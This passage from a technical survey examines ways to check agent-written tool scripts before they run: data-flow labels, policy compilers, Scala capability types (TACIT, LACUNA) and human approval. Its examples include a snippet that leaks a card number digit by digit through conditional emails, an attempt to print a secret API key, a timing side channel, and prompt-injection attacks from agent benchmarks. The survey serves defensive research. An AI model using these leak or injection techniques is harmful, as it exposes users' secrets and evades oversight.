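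The shop also has a rule that each email goes to the customer who was charged. If the model had written line 6 with `to=duplicates[0]["email"]`, all 40 emails would go to one person. The address would still carry the label "email", as in the correct script, because the labels record only which kind of data reaches the tool, not whose it is.

A finer analysis can also track which record a value came from, so it would reject the faulty version and accept the original. It still can't show that the address reaches the person who paid, because that is a fact about the shop's customers. The address in the record may be out of date, or it may belong to an assistant who booked the tickets for somebody else. The gate can enforce a substitute rule, that the address comes from the same record as the charge, but the shop has to decide whether that is close enough.

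### Where the analysis loses precision or fails

Rice's theorem implies that no analysis of this kind can be exact for every program, so a conservative analysis over-approximates by attaching labels that may be irrelevant. Certain code constructs greatly increase this over-approximation.

If the script chooses a tool based on fetched data, as in `tools[c["action"]](c["id"])`, the analyser can assume that the call might go to any tool in the collection. With the shop's three tools, the reviewer still learns that the line may refund or email something, but would learn almost nothing with the more than 1,800 tools in Dunkel's system.

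A static analyser can't read code that a script builds while running, because that code doesn't exist yet. *ACaM* (2026), a system that derives what agents and their tools can do from source code, excludes such code from its scope, along with code that modifies itself after deployment, deliberately obscured code, and remote components whose source isn't available. Many runtimes forbid code generated at run time. *MM-ToolSandBox* (2026), an environment for testing agents, rejects disallowed imports and unsafe functions before any Python runs, and applies further limits during the run. Dunkel's runtime also forbids dynamic evaluation. A restricted language can go further and make such constructions impossible to write.

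A script can also leak data without copying it:

```python
if c["card"].startswith("4"):
    await send_email(to="someone@example.com", text="yes")
```

The email contains no part of the card number, but its arrival reveals the first digit. With enough such tests, a script could send the whole number. *ACE*, like Girrens and Wang, therefore adds a condition's labels to everything that happens under it. Girrens and Wang check both branches this way because the analyser can't determine which one will run.

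This precaution would block a better refund script. The current one may refund guests without an account who were never charged twice. The model could fix this by comparing card numbers in line 2 instead of customers:

```python
keys = [(c["card"], c["amount"]) for c in charges]
```

The script now uses the card numbers to choose who receives an email, so every email carries the label "card" and the gate rejects the script, even though the emails mention only an amount. An analyser that ignored conditions would accept the improved script, but it would also accept the digit-by-digit leak.

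Coarse labels cause a similar problem. If the shop gave the whole result of `list_charges` a single label because it contains card numbers, the address and the amount would carry that label too, and the gate would reject the original script. Labels on individual fields avoid this but can still be too coarse. Customers may want to read "refunded to your card ending in 1234", and those four digits still carry the label "card". The policy would need an exception for the output of a trusted masking function. *Agent Audit* (2026), which applies source-to-sink analysis to the code of agent applications, similarly lowers its confidence in a finding if the code cleans the data on the way, for instance by escaping text before passing it to a command line.

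Language models can sometimes fill gaps in a static analysis. *ACaM* uses one for the small share of decisions that need judgement about meaning, but the model's answer can't weaken a fact that static analysis has established. Static analysis does all the data-flow tracing, because models tend to lose intermediate steps in long chains.

### When a script acts on data that others wrote

Labels can describe how far the shop trusts data as well as how sensitive it is. Girrens and Wang give every value both kinds of label. When a plan combines values, the result is as confidential as the most confidential input and only as trustworthy as the least trustworthy one. The same rule applies when data passes through a language model, so a summary of an untrusted email remains untrusted. Each tool has a minimum level of trust for its inputs, and the checker rejects any plan that would give a tool less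 trusted data.

The refund script would probably fail such a check. Customers create charges by buying things, so a strict policy would treat the charge records as untrusted and `issue_refund` as a tool that requires trusted inputs. Line 5 breaks that policy because its arguments come from untrusted data and because the loop around it uses untrusted data to determine which refunds to issue. The risk is real, since a customer can exploit the script by deliberately buying the same voucher twice. But the policy would also reject almost any script that looks something up and then acts on it.

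Girrens and Wang tested this check on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in which attackers plant instructions in the data that agents read. Turning the check on reduced the share of tasks completed from 53.0% to 29.0%. It stopped about 53% of all trials, typically because untrusted tool output would have reached a tool with a higher trust requirement. Successful attacks fell from four in 949 to none. The benchmark probably understates the benefit because its attacks mostly rely on planted instructions, which can't change a plan completed before the agent reads any data, even without the check. An attack that only falsified an account number would test the trust check better.

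Girrens and Wang suggest recovering some of the lost tasks with labels for individual fields, separate trust requirements for each argument, and explicit checks that raise a value's trust. The shop could, for example, trust a charge number once the payment system has confirmed that the same card paid the same amount twice within a minute. The concert tickets would pass this test, and somebody would still have to decide that it is good enough.

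### How a policy can be wrong

An analyser can trace every value correctly and still make the wrong decision if the policy is wrong. Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* describes a simple policy with a source (the result of the tool that fetches emails), a sink (the body of an outgoing email) and a condition (the recipient is outside the company). Existing tools such as CodeQL can search a script for a path that matches the policy. If the recipient's address is written into the script, the analyser can evaluate the condition immediately. In the refund script the address is data, so the condition has to be checked at run time. Meijer expects some checks to remain for run time and compares this to Java, which verifies a program before running it but still checks every array index during the run.

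Meijer also shows how a policy can be too weak. A user asks an agent to delete two files, `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the specification requires only that both be gone afterwards. A program that deletes every text file meets that specification. Similarly, in the shop, "every duplicate charge has been refunded" would be true even if a script refunded all 1,200 charges. A *frame condition* fixes this by requiring everything the user didn't mention to stay unchanged.

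Most organisations write their rules in prose, so the rules have to be translated into a form that software can check. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) presents a compiler for this. A language model reads each clause of a policy and proposes rules, each consisting of a condition and the tools it applies to. For example, "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" becomes a ban on using the flight-change tool when the cabin is basic economy. The model does this five times. Ordinary software then checks each proposed rule against the list of tools and their arguments, and only rules that appear in most of the runs are kept. A gate uses the finished rules to check one call at a time, without a language model. In a script, this gate would run at each call, so the static analysis applies to the policy rather than the script.

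The checks repaired or rejected 29 of 79 candidate rules for an airline and 7 of 53 for a retailer:

| Defect in the candidate rule | Airline | Retail |
|---|---|---|
| Applies to all tools and can't be narrowed down | 11 | 2 |
| Reads an argument that the tool doesn't have | 8 | 1 |
| Sets a condition that no available tool can fulfil | 5 | 0 |
| Demands the user's confirmation for merely reading data | 5 | 0 |
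| Blocks the very tool that would fulfil its condition | 0 | 4 |

The last row comes from the clause requiring the agent to authenticate the user first. The model turned it into a rule that blocked every tool until the user was authenticated, including the two lookup tools that perform the authentication, so no conversation could have got past that point. The software repaired the rule by exempting those two tools. It also merged duplicates and dropped proposals with too few votes, which left 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules.

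These checks are still needed with a stronger model. When Yu and colleagues had a frontier model extract the rules, one of the results would have blocked every call in the airline domain. The checks examine rules one at a time, so they miss deadlocks in which two rules each block the tool the other needs.

A rule can also be well formed and mean the opposite of the policy. A telecom company's policy required agents to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request. The compiler produced a rule that banned payment requests while a bill was overdue, the only time they should be sent. To find such errors, Yu and colleagues replayed the rules over recorded conversations in which an agent without a gate had completed its task. The faulty rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests. The same condition on a different tool would have refused none of 44 calls, so the error was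 in pairing that condition with the payment-request tool.

Yu and colleagues tested the gate on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which agents handle customer service under a written policy. They judged violations by a separate set of handwritten rules:

| | Airline, no gate | Airline, gate | Retail, no gate | Retail, gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changes that broke the policy | 66.3% | 2.6% | 30.8% | 6.9% |
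| Tasks solved in a single attempt | 39.2% | 47.6% | 52.4% | 50.2% |
| Tasks solved in each of four attempts | 21.2% | 34.4% | 24.6% | 22.8% |

The only statistically significant difference in task success is the airline domain's improvement over four attempts. A gate can plausibly help there, because a forbidden change to a booking also counts as a failed task. The gate also reduced the number of changes the agent made in the airline domain from 353 to 116. Of the 40 violations that remained in retail, 21 fell under two clauses that the gate couldn't enforce because the compiler had produced no rule for them.

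The violation rates also depend on how one reads the policy, and the same ambiguity would affect the refund script. Both policies require the user's confirmation before a change. Yu and colleagues let each confirmation cover one change, so the shop would need 80 confirmations for 40 refunds and 40 emails. If one confirmation may cover an announced batch, the violation rates without a gate drop to 36.8% and 13.6%. About half of the original violations therefore depended on interpretation, which no analysis of the rules or the script can settle.

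On AgentDojo's banking tasks, the gate reduced successful attacks from 46.5% to zero, but the share of tasks completed when there was no attack also fell, from 79.2% to 70.8%. One of its rules allows payments only to recipients the user has named or previously paid. This rule stops transfers to an attacker, but it also blocks payment of a genuine bill if the account number appears only in the bill. A similar rule for emails would block the refund script, which gets all its recipients from data.

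Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, use heavier machinery. A language model writes the policy as a program, together with a contract that states what must hold before and after the program runs. A verifier then tries to prove

{precondition} policy program {postcondition}

and returns counterexamples until the model has corrected the program or reached a limit on attempts. The proof covers more than the structural checks of Yu and colleagues do, but only relative to the contract. If the shop meant a limit of 40 dollars and the contract allows 400, the proof succeeds anyway. At run time, a language model also extracts the policy program's arguments from the agent's data, and the proof doesn't cover that step. A verified program can therefore judge a refund by the wrong amount.

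*ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) expresses its policy as logical rules over facts about tools. One example rule denies any tool that can both run shell commands and use the network. The facts come from each tool's description, traces of it running, and its source code. In a test on 16 tools, half of them malicious, the rules reached 88% accuracy using descriptions and traces. Adding source code exposed more dangerous behaviour but also led the rules to block more harmless tools with powerful functions.

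Their system also judges calls in the context of a task, and it classified all 20 test scenarios for this correctly. A scoring program and a language model did equally well, so the test doesn't show that logical rules are better. But removing the rules about combinations of calls made the results much worse. Reading private data and contacting an outside server can each be harmless, and a policy that considers only one call at a time will miss the danger of doing both.

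### What is known about error rates

No one appears to have published false positive or false negative rates for static checks on tool-orchestration scripts. Girrens and Wang's data on rejected plans are the closest, since an agent wrote the plans, which contain loops and branches. But their figures don't separate harmless plans from harmful ones, and the plans are in a restricted planning language rather than Python or JavaScript.

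*Look Before You Leap* (Althoubi, 2026) measured false negative and false positive rates for a checker of single shell commands, using 9,930 commands for 482 tools. The checker caught 95.8% of the invalid commands, a false negative rate of 4.2%, and wrongly rejected 10.0% of the valid ones. Checking only the syntax and whether the program exists produced no false positives but caught just half of the errors. All 198 false positives occurred because the checker's description of the tools lacked real options that it had failed to extract from their help texts. A team that forgets to declare a field or a tool should expect the same kind of error.

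Althoubi's checker tests whether a command is valid, not whether it is allowed, so it would pass a correctly written command to delete the wrong folder. Valid form also isn't a good sign that a program does its job. *RubricRefine* (2026) describes a checker that compares the tool calls in agents' code with the documented arguments. Using its scores to pick the best of several candidate programs gave worse results than plain CodeAct with every model tested, though an analyser that also traced data might do better.

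Other measurements concern software that people maintain. In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) searched 6,549 agent projects for loops that might never end because a model's or tool's output decides whether they continue. Of 74 warnings, 68 were correct, but this doesn't show how many such loops the search missed. In *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) tested their rules on 217 known vulnerabilities in an agent's own code and found 66.8% with one analysis tool and 75.1% with another. On current code, the rules produced so many doubtful warnings that people had to sort through them by hand.

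Agent-written scripts might be easier to analyse than these projects, because they are short and mostly call tools whose effects somebody can declare in advance. They might also be harder, because a model writes each one from scratch and nobody cleans it up. A team could estimate its own false positive rate by running its gate on past scripts that turned out to be harmless, much as Yu and colleagues ran their rules on old conversations. The false negative rate is harder to estimate, because the team would need harmful scripts that resemble what its agent might write.

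## Restricted languages in which unsafe scripts do not compile

A static analyser for Python must handle everything Python allows, and it loses precision when a script picks its tools by name or builds code as it runs. A restricted language omits these constructs. The model has to write its scripts in a form that software can check completely, and a script that fails the check does not run.

Ordinary typed languages already reject some unsafe scripts before they run. A *type* records what kind of value a name stands for, such as text, a number, or a charge with five fields. A *compiler*, the software that translates source code into something a computer can run, first checks that the types fit together. Suppose the model misspells the email field in line 6 of the refund script as `c["emial"]`. Python would list the charges, issue the first refund and then crash. In a typed language with declared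 fields for charges, the script would not compile, so it would issue no refunds.

The compiler reaches this result without examining any charges, so the result holds for every list the payment system could return. Misspelled fields are an easy case, but for the compiler to act as a gate against unsafe scripts, the types must also record what a piece of code can do to the outside world.

### Capabilities and capture sets

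Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) built such a gate, TACIT, at the Swiss university EPFL and describe it in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*. TACIT gives an agent a tool that accepts a Scala 3 script, compiles it, and runs it only if compilation succeeds. It is an MCP server, so existing agents can connect to it without changes.

TACIT relies on *capabilities*, an idea that dates from 1966. A capability is a program value that a script must hold to use a resource. In the *object-capability* model, it is an ordinary object, such as one representing a folder or a mail account. Code can use the mail account only if it has received the object for it, and it can't forge that object from a name or a number.

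Handing out objects limits what a whole script can reach, but it doesn't show which part of the script uses what. Scala 3 has an experimental feature, *capture checking*, that records this in the types. Take a function that writes a piece of text to a file `f`:

```scala
(s: String) => f.write(s)
```

Its type is `String ->{f} Unit`. The function takes text, returns nothing useful (`Unit`), and may use `f`. The part in braces is its *capture set*, which the compiler works out from the code. Functions from text to `Unit` can have three kinds of type:

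| Type | What the function may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Unit` | no capability at all (a *pure* function) |
| `String ->{f} Unit` | `f` and nothing else |
| `String => Unit` | any capability |

A capture set is an over-approximation. If the function writes to `f` only when the text is longer than a page, `f` is in the set anyway. In return, the following holds for every input *d*:

capabilities used on *d* ⊆ capture set

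This is the same kind of condition as for a closure-bound approval, with the capture set in place of the approval record. The compiler accepts a function only where the program permits everything in the function's capture set. It therefore accepts a pure function anywhere, but rejects a function that writes to `f` where the program requires a pure one.

### A wrapper that only pure functions can open

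TACIT uses that last rule to protect secrets. It returns sensitive data inside a wrapper called `Classified`, whose central method is `map`:

```scala
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` is the type of the hidden content. A script can pass `map` a function `op` that computes something from the content, and `map` wraps the result. The thin arrow in `T -> U` means that `op` must be pure. Odersky and colleagues call the ability to forbid effects in one part of a program while allowing them elsewhere *local purity*.

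In this example, the script reads an access key from a protected file:

```scala
val key = readClassified("/secrets/api-keys/github.txt")
key.map(k => k.trim)                           // accepted
key.map(k => println(s"GitHub API Key: $k"))   // rejected
```

The function in the second line removes spaces around the key. It uses no capability, so its type is `String -> String` and the wrapper accepts it. The function in the third line prints the key. Printed text goes back to the agent's model, so TACIT treats printing as an effect that needs a capability. The compiler finds the type `String ->{x$1} Unit`, where `x$1` is its name for that capability. The wrapper requires `String -> Unit`, so the compiler rejects the whole script. An agent in TACIT's tests submitted code like the third line and received this error.

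A script can still write wrapped data to another protected file or send it to a second language model that the operator trusts, which returns a wrapped answer. It can also print the data. The user's terminal then shows the content, while the agent's model receives only `Classified(****)`. The data stays wrapped in later turns. If the user asks how long a secret summary is, the agent can compute the length, but the number is wrapped too.

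### Access that can't leave its block

Scripts also need ordinary files, and TACIT grants access to them for the length of a block:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/data") { fs => fs.access("report.txt").read() }        // accepted
requestFileSystem("/data") { fs => () => fs.access("secret.txt").read() }  // rejected
```

Here `fs` is a capability for the folder `/data`. The first block reads a file and returns its text, which captures nothing. The second returns a function that would read a file later, after access should have ended. That function's type has `fs` in its capture set, but the type of a block's result must be valid outside the block, where `fs` doesn't exist, so the compiler rejects the script.

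Commands and network connections work the same way, with a list of permitted commands or hosts in place of the folder. The compiler can't check a path that the script computes from data, so TACIT's library checks paths during the run and refuses any outside the folder. In the published interface, the script itself names the folder or hosts to be used. A reviewer can read the line that names them quickly, but an operator who wants fixed limits has to build them into the library.

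All these guarantees would fail if a script could make the compiler drop a capture set. Some Scala features can do this, such as casts, which tell the compiler to treat a value as another type, and reflection, which looks up parts of a program by name at run time. *Safe mode* forbids these features in agent-written code and limits the script to safe library code. It still allows exceptions, since a division by zero can raise one anywhere. A secret could escape in an error message, so TACIT catches exceptions at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which can be wrapped like any others.

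The type system underlying capture checking has computer-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues note that an argument covering safe mode is still missing. The implementation has also lagged behind the design. lampepfl's *TACIT*, the project's documentation, describes an early version that enforced safe mode by searching scripts for forbidden text patterns, with a planned move to the compiler's own safe mode.

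### TACIT's test results

Odersky and colleagues tested whether secrets leak by giving agents a software project with a folder of keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections each, and added 11 malicious requests from the user, five of them direct and six posing as a trusted authority. This made 131 trials, which they ran with two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once as plain text. The table shows the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

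| | Trials | Wrapped | Plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, injections | 120 | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious requests | 11 | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, all | 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, injections | 120 | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious requests | 11 | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, all | 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Ten of the 13 leaks came from the malicious requests, where the user asked for the secrets. The injections were a weak test, since Claude resisted all 120 even without the types. The better argument for TACIT is that its guarantee doesn't depend on the model. The trials mainly test whether the implementation has an obvious hole.

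Wrapping the secrets didn't reduce the agents' usefulness. Claude completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with wrapped secrets and 83.3% with plain ones. MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%, respectively. Odersky and colleagues suspect their setup explains part of Claude's gap, because Claude often ran out of time or turns. It also sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

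They also ported AgentDojo's four domains to TACIT and ran them with two other models. Of about 1,900 attacks, one counted as successful. In that attack, a planted hotel review recommended a different hotel. The agent booked the right one but quoted the review to the user, which AgentDojo scores as a successful attack. Agents completed between 40% and 69% of the tasks, depending on domain and model. The comparison includes no undefended agent, so it doesn't show how the protection affected task completion. CaMeL, a system that tracks data while the code runs, did about as well in most domains, but with one model it completed 81.4% of the office tasks against TACIT's 52.9%.

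For the cost in task success, the better evidence is τ²-bench, where each model worked once with ordinary tool calls and once by writing typed Scala. The success rates are averages over ten runs per task:

| | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
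| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Scala did slightly better in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to structured results and helpful error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, probably because repairing code relies more on shell commands.

Only 0.32% to 7.93% of the τ²-bench snippets needed a retry after the compiler rejected them, and those took 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Many of the rejected snippets were simply broken, so these rates aren't false positive rates. Checking a snippet takes less than a second once the compiler has warmed up. Models often wrote prices such as `$50` incorrectly in Scala's text templates, where a dollar sign introduces a variable and the price has to be written `$$50`. The same error can easily occur in an email about a refund, but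 it only leads to a retry, since the compiler's message shows what to fix.

### LACUNA and permission by scope

In TACIT, the model writes a script and the compiler checks it in a prepared environment. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, mostly from the same group, put the model's code inside a larger program that a developer has written. The developer leaves a gap by calling `agent`, with a task in plain language and the type of result the program needs. In the shop, it might look like this:

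```scala
def refundAll(duplicates: List[Charge])(using Payments): Int =
  agent[Int]("Refund these charges and return how many there were")
```

The words `using Payments` mean that this function can run only where the program holds a capability for payments. When execution reaches the gap, four things happen:

1. LACUNA sends the model the task, the required type, the surrounding code, and the names and types of all variables available at that point.
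2. The model writes Scala code to fill the gap.
3. The compiler checks the code as if the developer had typed it there.
4. If the check succeeds, the code runs. Otherwise the model receives the error messages and tries again, up to a limit.

The variables in scope at the gap are therefore the agent's permissions. The code that fills this gap can use `duplicates` and issue refunds. It can't send an email if sending requires a mail capability and none is in scope, whatever instructions the model has read. The developer sets the permissions by choosing where to put the gap, and can give different steps of a program different permissions.

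The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, the program has a balance of 100, and the model writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects both lines, so the balance stays at 100. Python would have run the subtraction before the error was detected. This protects only against errors the compiler can find, so if a payment service fails partway through a set of refunds, some customers will still have been refunded and others not.

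The code in a gap can contain further `agent` calls, which the model fills only when execution reaches them, so no one can read the complete program before it runs. Earlier parts may already have had effects by the time the compiler checks a later one. LACUNA limits what each step can reach, but it is therefore less useful than TACIT to a reviewer who wants to approve a whole script in advance.

Zhao and colleagues first tested the compiler on about 400 prepared cases, each combining developer code with a correct or faulty snippet, and it gave the intended result every time. They then ran agents on BrowseComp-Plus, which has 830 hard research questions over a fixed collection of documents. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated snippets, an average of 0.7 retries per question, and the agent answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. They did not compare it with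 an untyped agent on this benchmark.

On τ²-bench there was one, and LACUNA solved fewer tasks overall with both models:

| | DeepSeek V4 Flash, tool calls | DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, tool calls | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% | 52.6% | 43.9% |
| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% | 56.0% | 38.0% |
| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% | 15.8% | 14.9% |
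| Telecom with workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% | 21.1% | 24.6% |
| All 392 tasks | 90.0% | 76.0% | 33.2% | 29.1% |

DeepSeek's 76.0% differs from its score with ordinary tool calling by 14 points, a large gap, although Zhao and colleagues describe the two as on par. The gap also contrasts with TACIT's results on the same benchmark. Either the design or the setup could explain that contrast, because the models differed and LACUNA's ran with reasoning switched off and only once per task.

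Rejections were also more common. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's retail snippets. For Gemini, it rejected 3.2% in retail and 89% in telecom, where most turns made no progress. The guarantee holds regardless of the model's strength, but a weak model may get little done. Models have seen much less Scala than Python, which Zhao and colleagues suspect is part of the problem.

Eight of about 1,900 AgentDojo attacks succeeded against LACUNA, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that types don't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability the task needs. In the shop, a planted instruction to refund one more charge would use the same `Payments` capability as the 40 correct refunds.

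### Tool programs without loops or arithmetic

A language can be restricted much further, until a program is only a list of calls. Kovalenko and Redchych, whose four declared effects came up earlier, let a model write several tool calls in one turn and refer in a later call to the result of an earlier one. With tools from their simulated shop, such a *tool program* might be:

```text
1  search_orders(customer="c_17")
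2  get_order(id="$1.orders[0].id")
```

The reference `$1.orders[0].id` stands for the identifier of the first order that call 1 returns. A program can select fields in this way but do nothing else. It has no conditions, loops or arithmetic, so every call and dependency is visible in the text.

The executor builds a graph of the calls. It adds an arrow from call 1 to call 2 if call 2 refers to the result of call 1, or if, according to the tools' declarations, one of them changes something that the other reads or changes. It then runs the calls in that order, and calls that don't depend on each other can run at the same time. Destructive calls, including refunds and emails, are allowed only in a turn after the user has confirmed them.

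The same declarations make a finished run easy to check. Kovalenko and Redchych call a run *effect-safe* if the user confirmed every destructive call, the agent did not repeat any write whose repetition would matter, and the agent read each thing before changing it. Software checks these conditions by replaying the calls, without a language model or human labels.

The refund script can't be written in this language, because line 3 compares charges and line 4 starts a loop. The shop could add a tool that finds duplicates and another that refunds a whole list. The program would then be two calls that a reviewer could understand at a glance. But the comparison and the loop would be inside the tools, and the single refund call could still refund three charges or three thousand.

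Kovalenko and Redchych used their declarations mainly to train small models. They generated correct example runs in a simulated office and trained the four-billion-parameter model Qwen3-4B on them, together with public data. The model's success rate rose in all three tests:

| Test | Tasks | Before training | After training |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office, familiar kinds of task | 498 | 53% | 99% |
| Office, with new kinds of task and distracting tools | 775 | 52% | 81% |
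| Online shop, unfamiliar tools | 547 | 74% | 83% |

These gains come from the training, so they aren't evidence that the restricted language makes agents more successful. On the familiar tasks, a trained model did equally well with tool programs and with one tool call per turn, but the programs needed 25% fewer model calls.

The results for confirmation are more relevant to a gate. In the familiar office tasks, the model made 94 destructive calls without confirmation before training, and a model trained on an earlier version of the data made none. In the unfamiliar shop, training raised the number of unconfirmed payments, cancellations and refunds from 7 to 24, and to 64 with a version of the training data meant to teach the model when to decline. Adding each tool's declared effect to its description lowered the 24 only to 19, a difference that could be due to chance.

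The model had apparently learned to ask for confirmation before using particular tools, rather than before destructive actions in general. The test counted violations after they happened, but a runtime with the same declarations could block every unconfirmed destructive call, including calls to tools new to the model.

### The refund script with types

To use TACIT, the shop would have to describe its tools in Scala. One possible interface is:

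```scala
case class Charge(id: String, customer: String, amount: Int,
                  email: String, card: Classified[String])

def listCharges(month: String): List[Charge]
def issueRefund(charge: String, amount: Int)(using Payments): Unit
def sendEmail(to: String, text: String)(using Mail): Unit
```

Only the card number is wrapped. A direct translation of the refund script compiles, since it never touches `card`. The table shows what would happen to six harmful variants:

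| Variant | Compiles? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Emails `c.card` to the customer | no | the text must be a `String`, and this is a `Classified[String]` |
| Calls `sendEmail` inside `c.card.map` | no | the function uses `Mail`, so it isn't pure |
| Sends an email only if the card number starts with 4 | no | the test gives a `Classified[Boolean]`, and `if` needs a plain `Boolean` |
| Refunds `2 * c.amount` | yes | twice an amount is still an `Int` |
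| Sends every email to the first customer | yes | every address is a `String` |
| Refunds all 1,200 charges | yes | `charges` and `duplicates` have the same type |

The wrapper prevents the third variant, the digit-by-digit leak, without any extra rule, whereas a label-based analyser had to add each condition's labels to everything under that condition.

The last three variants compile because the types describe kinds of values, and a wrong refund has the same kinds of values as a right one. As Zhao and colleagues write, "Well-typed is not correct". The original script also compiles, even though it refunds the second concert ticket.

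A better interface can exclude some wrong refunds. The shop could replace the last two functions with a single `refundAndNotify(charge: Charge)` and prevent scripts from creating `Charge` values. A script could then no longer double an amount or write to the wrong customer, because the function takes both the amount and the address from one record. It could still refund all 1,200 charges, so the library could grant a payment capability that stops working after 50 refunds. That limit would be checked at run time, as file paths are. Zhao and colleagues also hope to use types with conditions attached, such as "a whole number up to 40". A script would then compile only if the amount was provably within the limit.

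Wrapping too much data can stop a script from doing its job. If the shop also wrapped the amounts and addresses, the script couldn't pass them to `issueRefund` or `sendEmail`, so it couldn't issue any refunds. TACIT's version of the AgentDojo bank faces this problem because transactions arrive wrapped while the payment function takes plain values. The payment function's published signature lists no capability, and the agent's instructions mention effects inside `map`, so the port seems to have allowed payments there. This would keep the transactions from the agent's model but not from whoever receives a payment. *Safe Scala*, an introduction by the software consultancy VirtusLab, describes the same trade-off between classifying data and leaving the agent enough to work with.

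### What the guarantee depends on

The compiler checks only the script. If a script starts an external command, that command runs outside Scala, so the protection depends on which commands are permitted. Odersky and colleagues recommend keeping the list of permitted commands short and adding a sandbox. The compiler also can't check what a tool does on someone else's server. `Payments` controls who may call `issueRefund`, but not what the payment company does with the call. The protection also fails if the agent can reach the same resources another way, so the project's documentation advises users to switch off the agent's built-in file, shell and web tools.

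Timing can still leak information. A pure function can finish at once if a card number starts with 4 and run for a second otherwise, so anyone who can time the script learns one yes-or-no answer. Fifty-four such answers are enough to identify a 16-digit number, because 2⁵⁴ is larger than the 10¹⁶ possible values. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing from their guarantee, along with leaks through whether a program finishes.

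The library needs more attention because it has to do things that safe mode forbids. Its developers mark such code `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler accepts it without checking that it is safe. Scripts can't use this mark. Scala's documentation gives the example of a trusted mail object that shows each email to the user and sends it only after the user agrees. The refund script could call this object without changing its logic, and the user would see 40 prompts.

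Mistakes in trusted code can be subtle. Suppose the model improves the script by comparing card numbers instead of customers. In Scala, two objects normally count as different even if their contents match, so the script would compile, find no duplicates and refund nobody. The library's author might fix this by making two wrappers equal when their contents are equal. But the comparison would then return a plain yes or no, so a script could wrap one guess after another and check each against a customer's card number. It would be safer for `listCharges` to supply a random token for each card, which a script could compare freely.

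Writing the interfaces takes moderate effort. TACIT's reusable library has about 1,000 lines, and the airline and retail interfaces for τ²-bench have a few hundred lines each, which makes them about as long as the tool descriptions they replace. Agents can help write them. The shop's three tools would be a small job. For a catalogue like Dunkel's, with more than 1,800 tools, software could generate the signatures, but someone would still have to decide which results to wrap and which capability each tool requires. A wrong decision weakens the guarantee without causing a compiler error.

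The limited choice of language is another drawback. Odersky and colleagues consider Scala 3 the only production-ready language whose compiler tracks capabilities, while the OpenAI and Anthropic runtimes take JavaScript and Python. Haskell separates pure functions from those with effects, but it has no built-in object capabilities. Older capability languages such as E check access only at run time. Scala's documentation describes its capability-tracking feature, capture checking, as "still highly experimental and unstable".

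## Human approval of scripts

Some harmful variants of the refund script pass every check described so far, because a compiler has no information about which charges the shop meant to refund. Somebody at the shop may know, which is the main reason to ask a person to approve the script. How well that person can judge the script depends partly on what the approval request shows.

### What the reviewer sees

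An approval request can show the script itself or something shorter. For the refund script, the options might look like this:

| Shown to the reviewer | Content | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| Raw script | the seven lines | the number, amounts and recipients of the refunds |
| List of tool calls | `list_charges`, `issue_refund`, `send_email` | also the loop and the test for a duplicate |
| Model-written summary | "Refunds customers who were charged twice in November and emails them" | also any difference between what the model meant and what it wrote |
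| Plan | "Fetch the charges, find duplicates, refund and notify" | also how the script carries out each step |

The list of tool calls would be identical for a script that refunded all 1,200 charges. The summary is more readable, but it presents the second concert ticket as a double charge, because the model that wrote it had already treated it as one. Only the raw script contains the test, in line 3. To object to the test, the reviewer has to read Python and think of a customer who buys the same thing twice.

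Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, already asks people to approve a related kind of script. Anthropic's *Orchestrate subagents at scale with dynamic workflows* describes JavaScript programs that the model writes to coordinate dozens or hundreds of subagents and that keep intermediate results in variables. In the terminal, the approval prompt shows the planned phases and gives the option to view the raw script. The desktop app's approval card shows the workflow's name, its phases and a warning about token use.

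In *auto mode*, where an AI reviewer replaces most permission prompts, Claude Code asks for approval only before the first workflow. That approval covers all later workflows, including those whose scripts the model hasn't written yet. The agents that a workflow starts still go through permission checks for their own tool calls, so this approval isn't the last check, but it would be for the refund script unless the runtime also checked each call.

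### One dangerous command among routine prompts

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports a large controlled test of human approval. Through a research vendor, the company hired 1,053 professional testers for what they understood to be a coding study. They worked in an environment built for the study and knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. The vendor recorded whether the tester approved it, and the command never ran.

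The testers blocked 143 of the 1,053 commands, or 13.6%. The classifier, which is auto mode's AI reviewer, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Anthropic also reports how many commands only one of the two blocked, and the remaining numbers follow by subtraction:

| | Person blocked | Person approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
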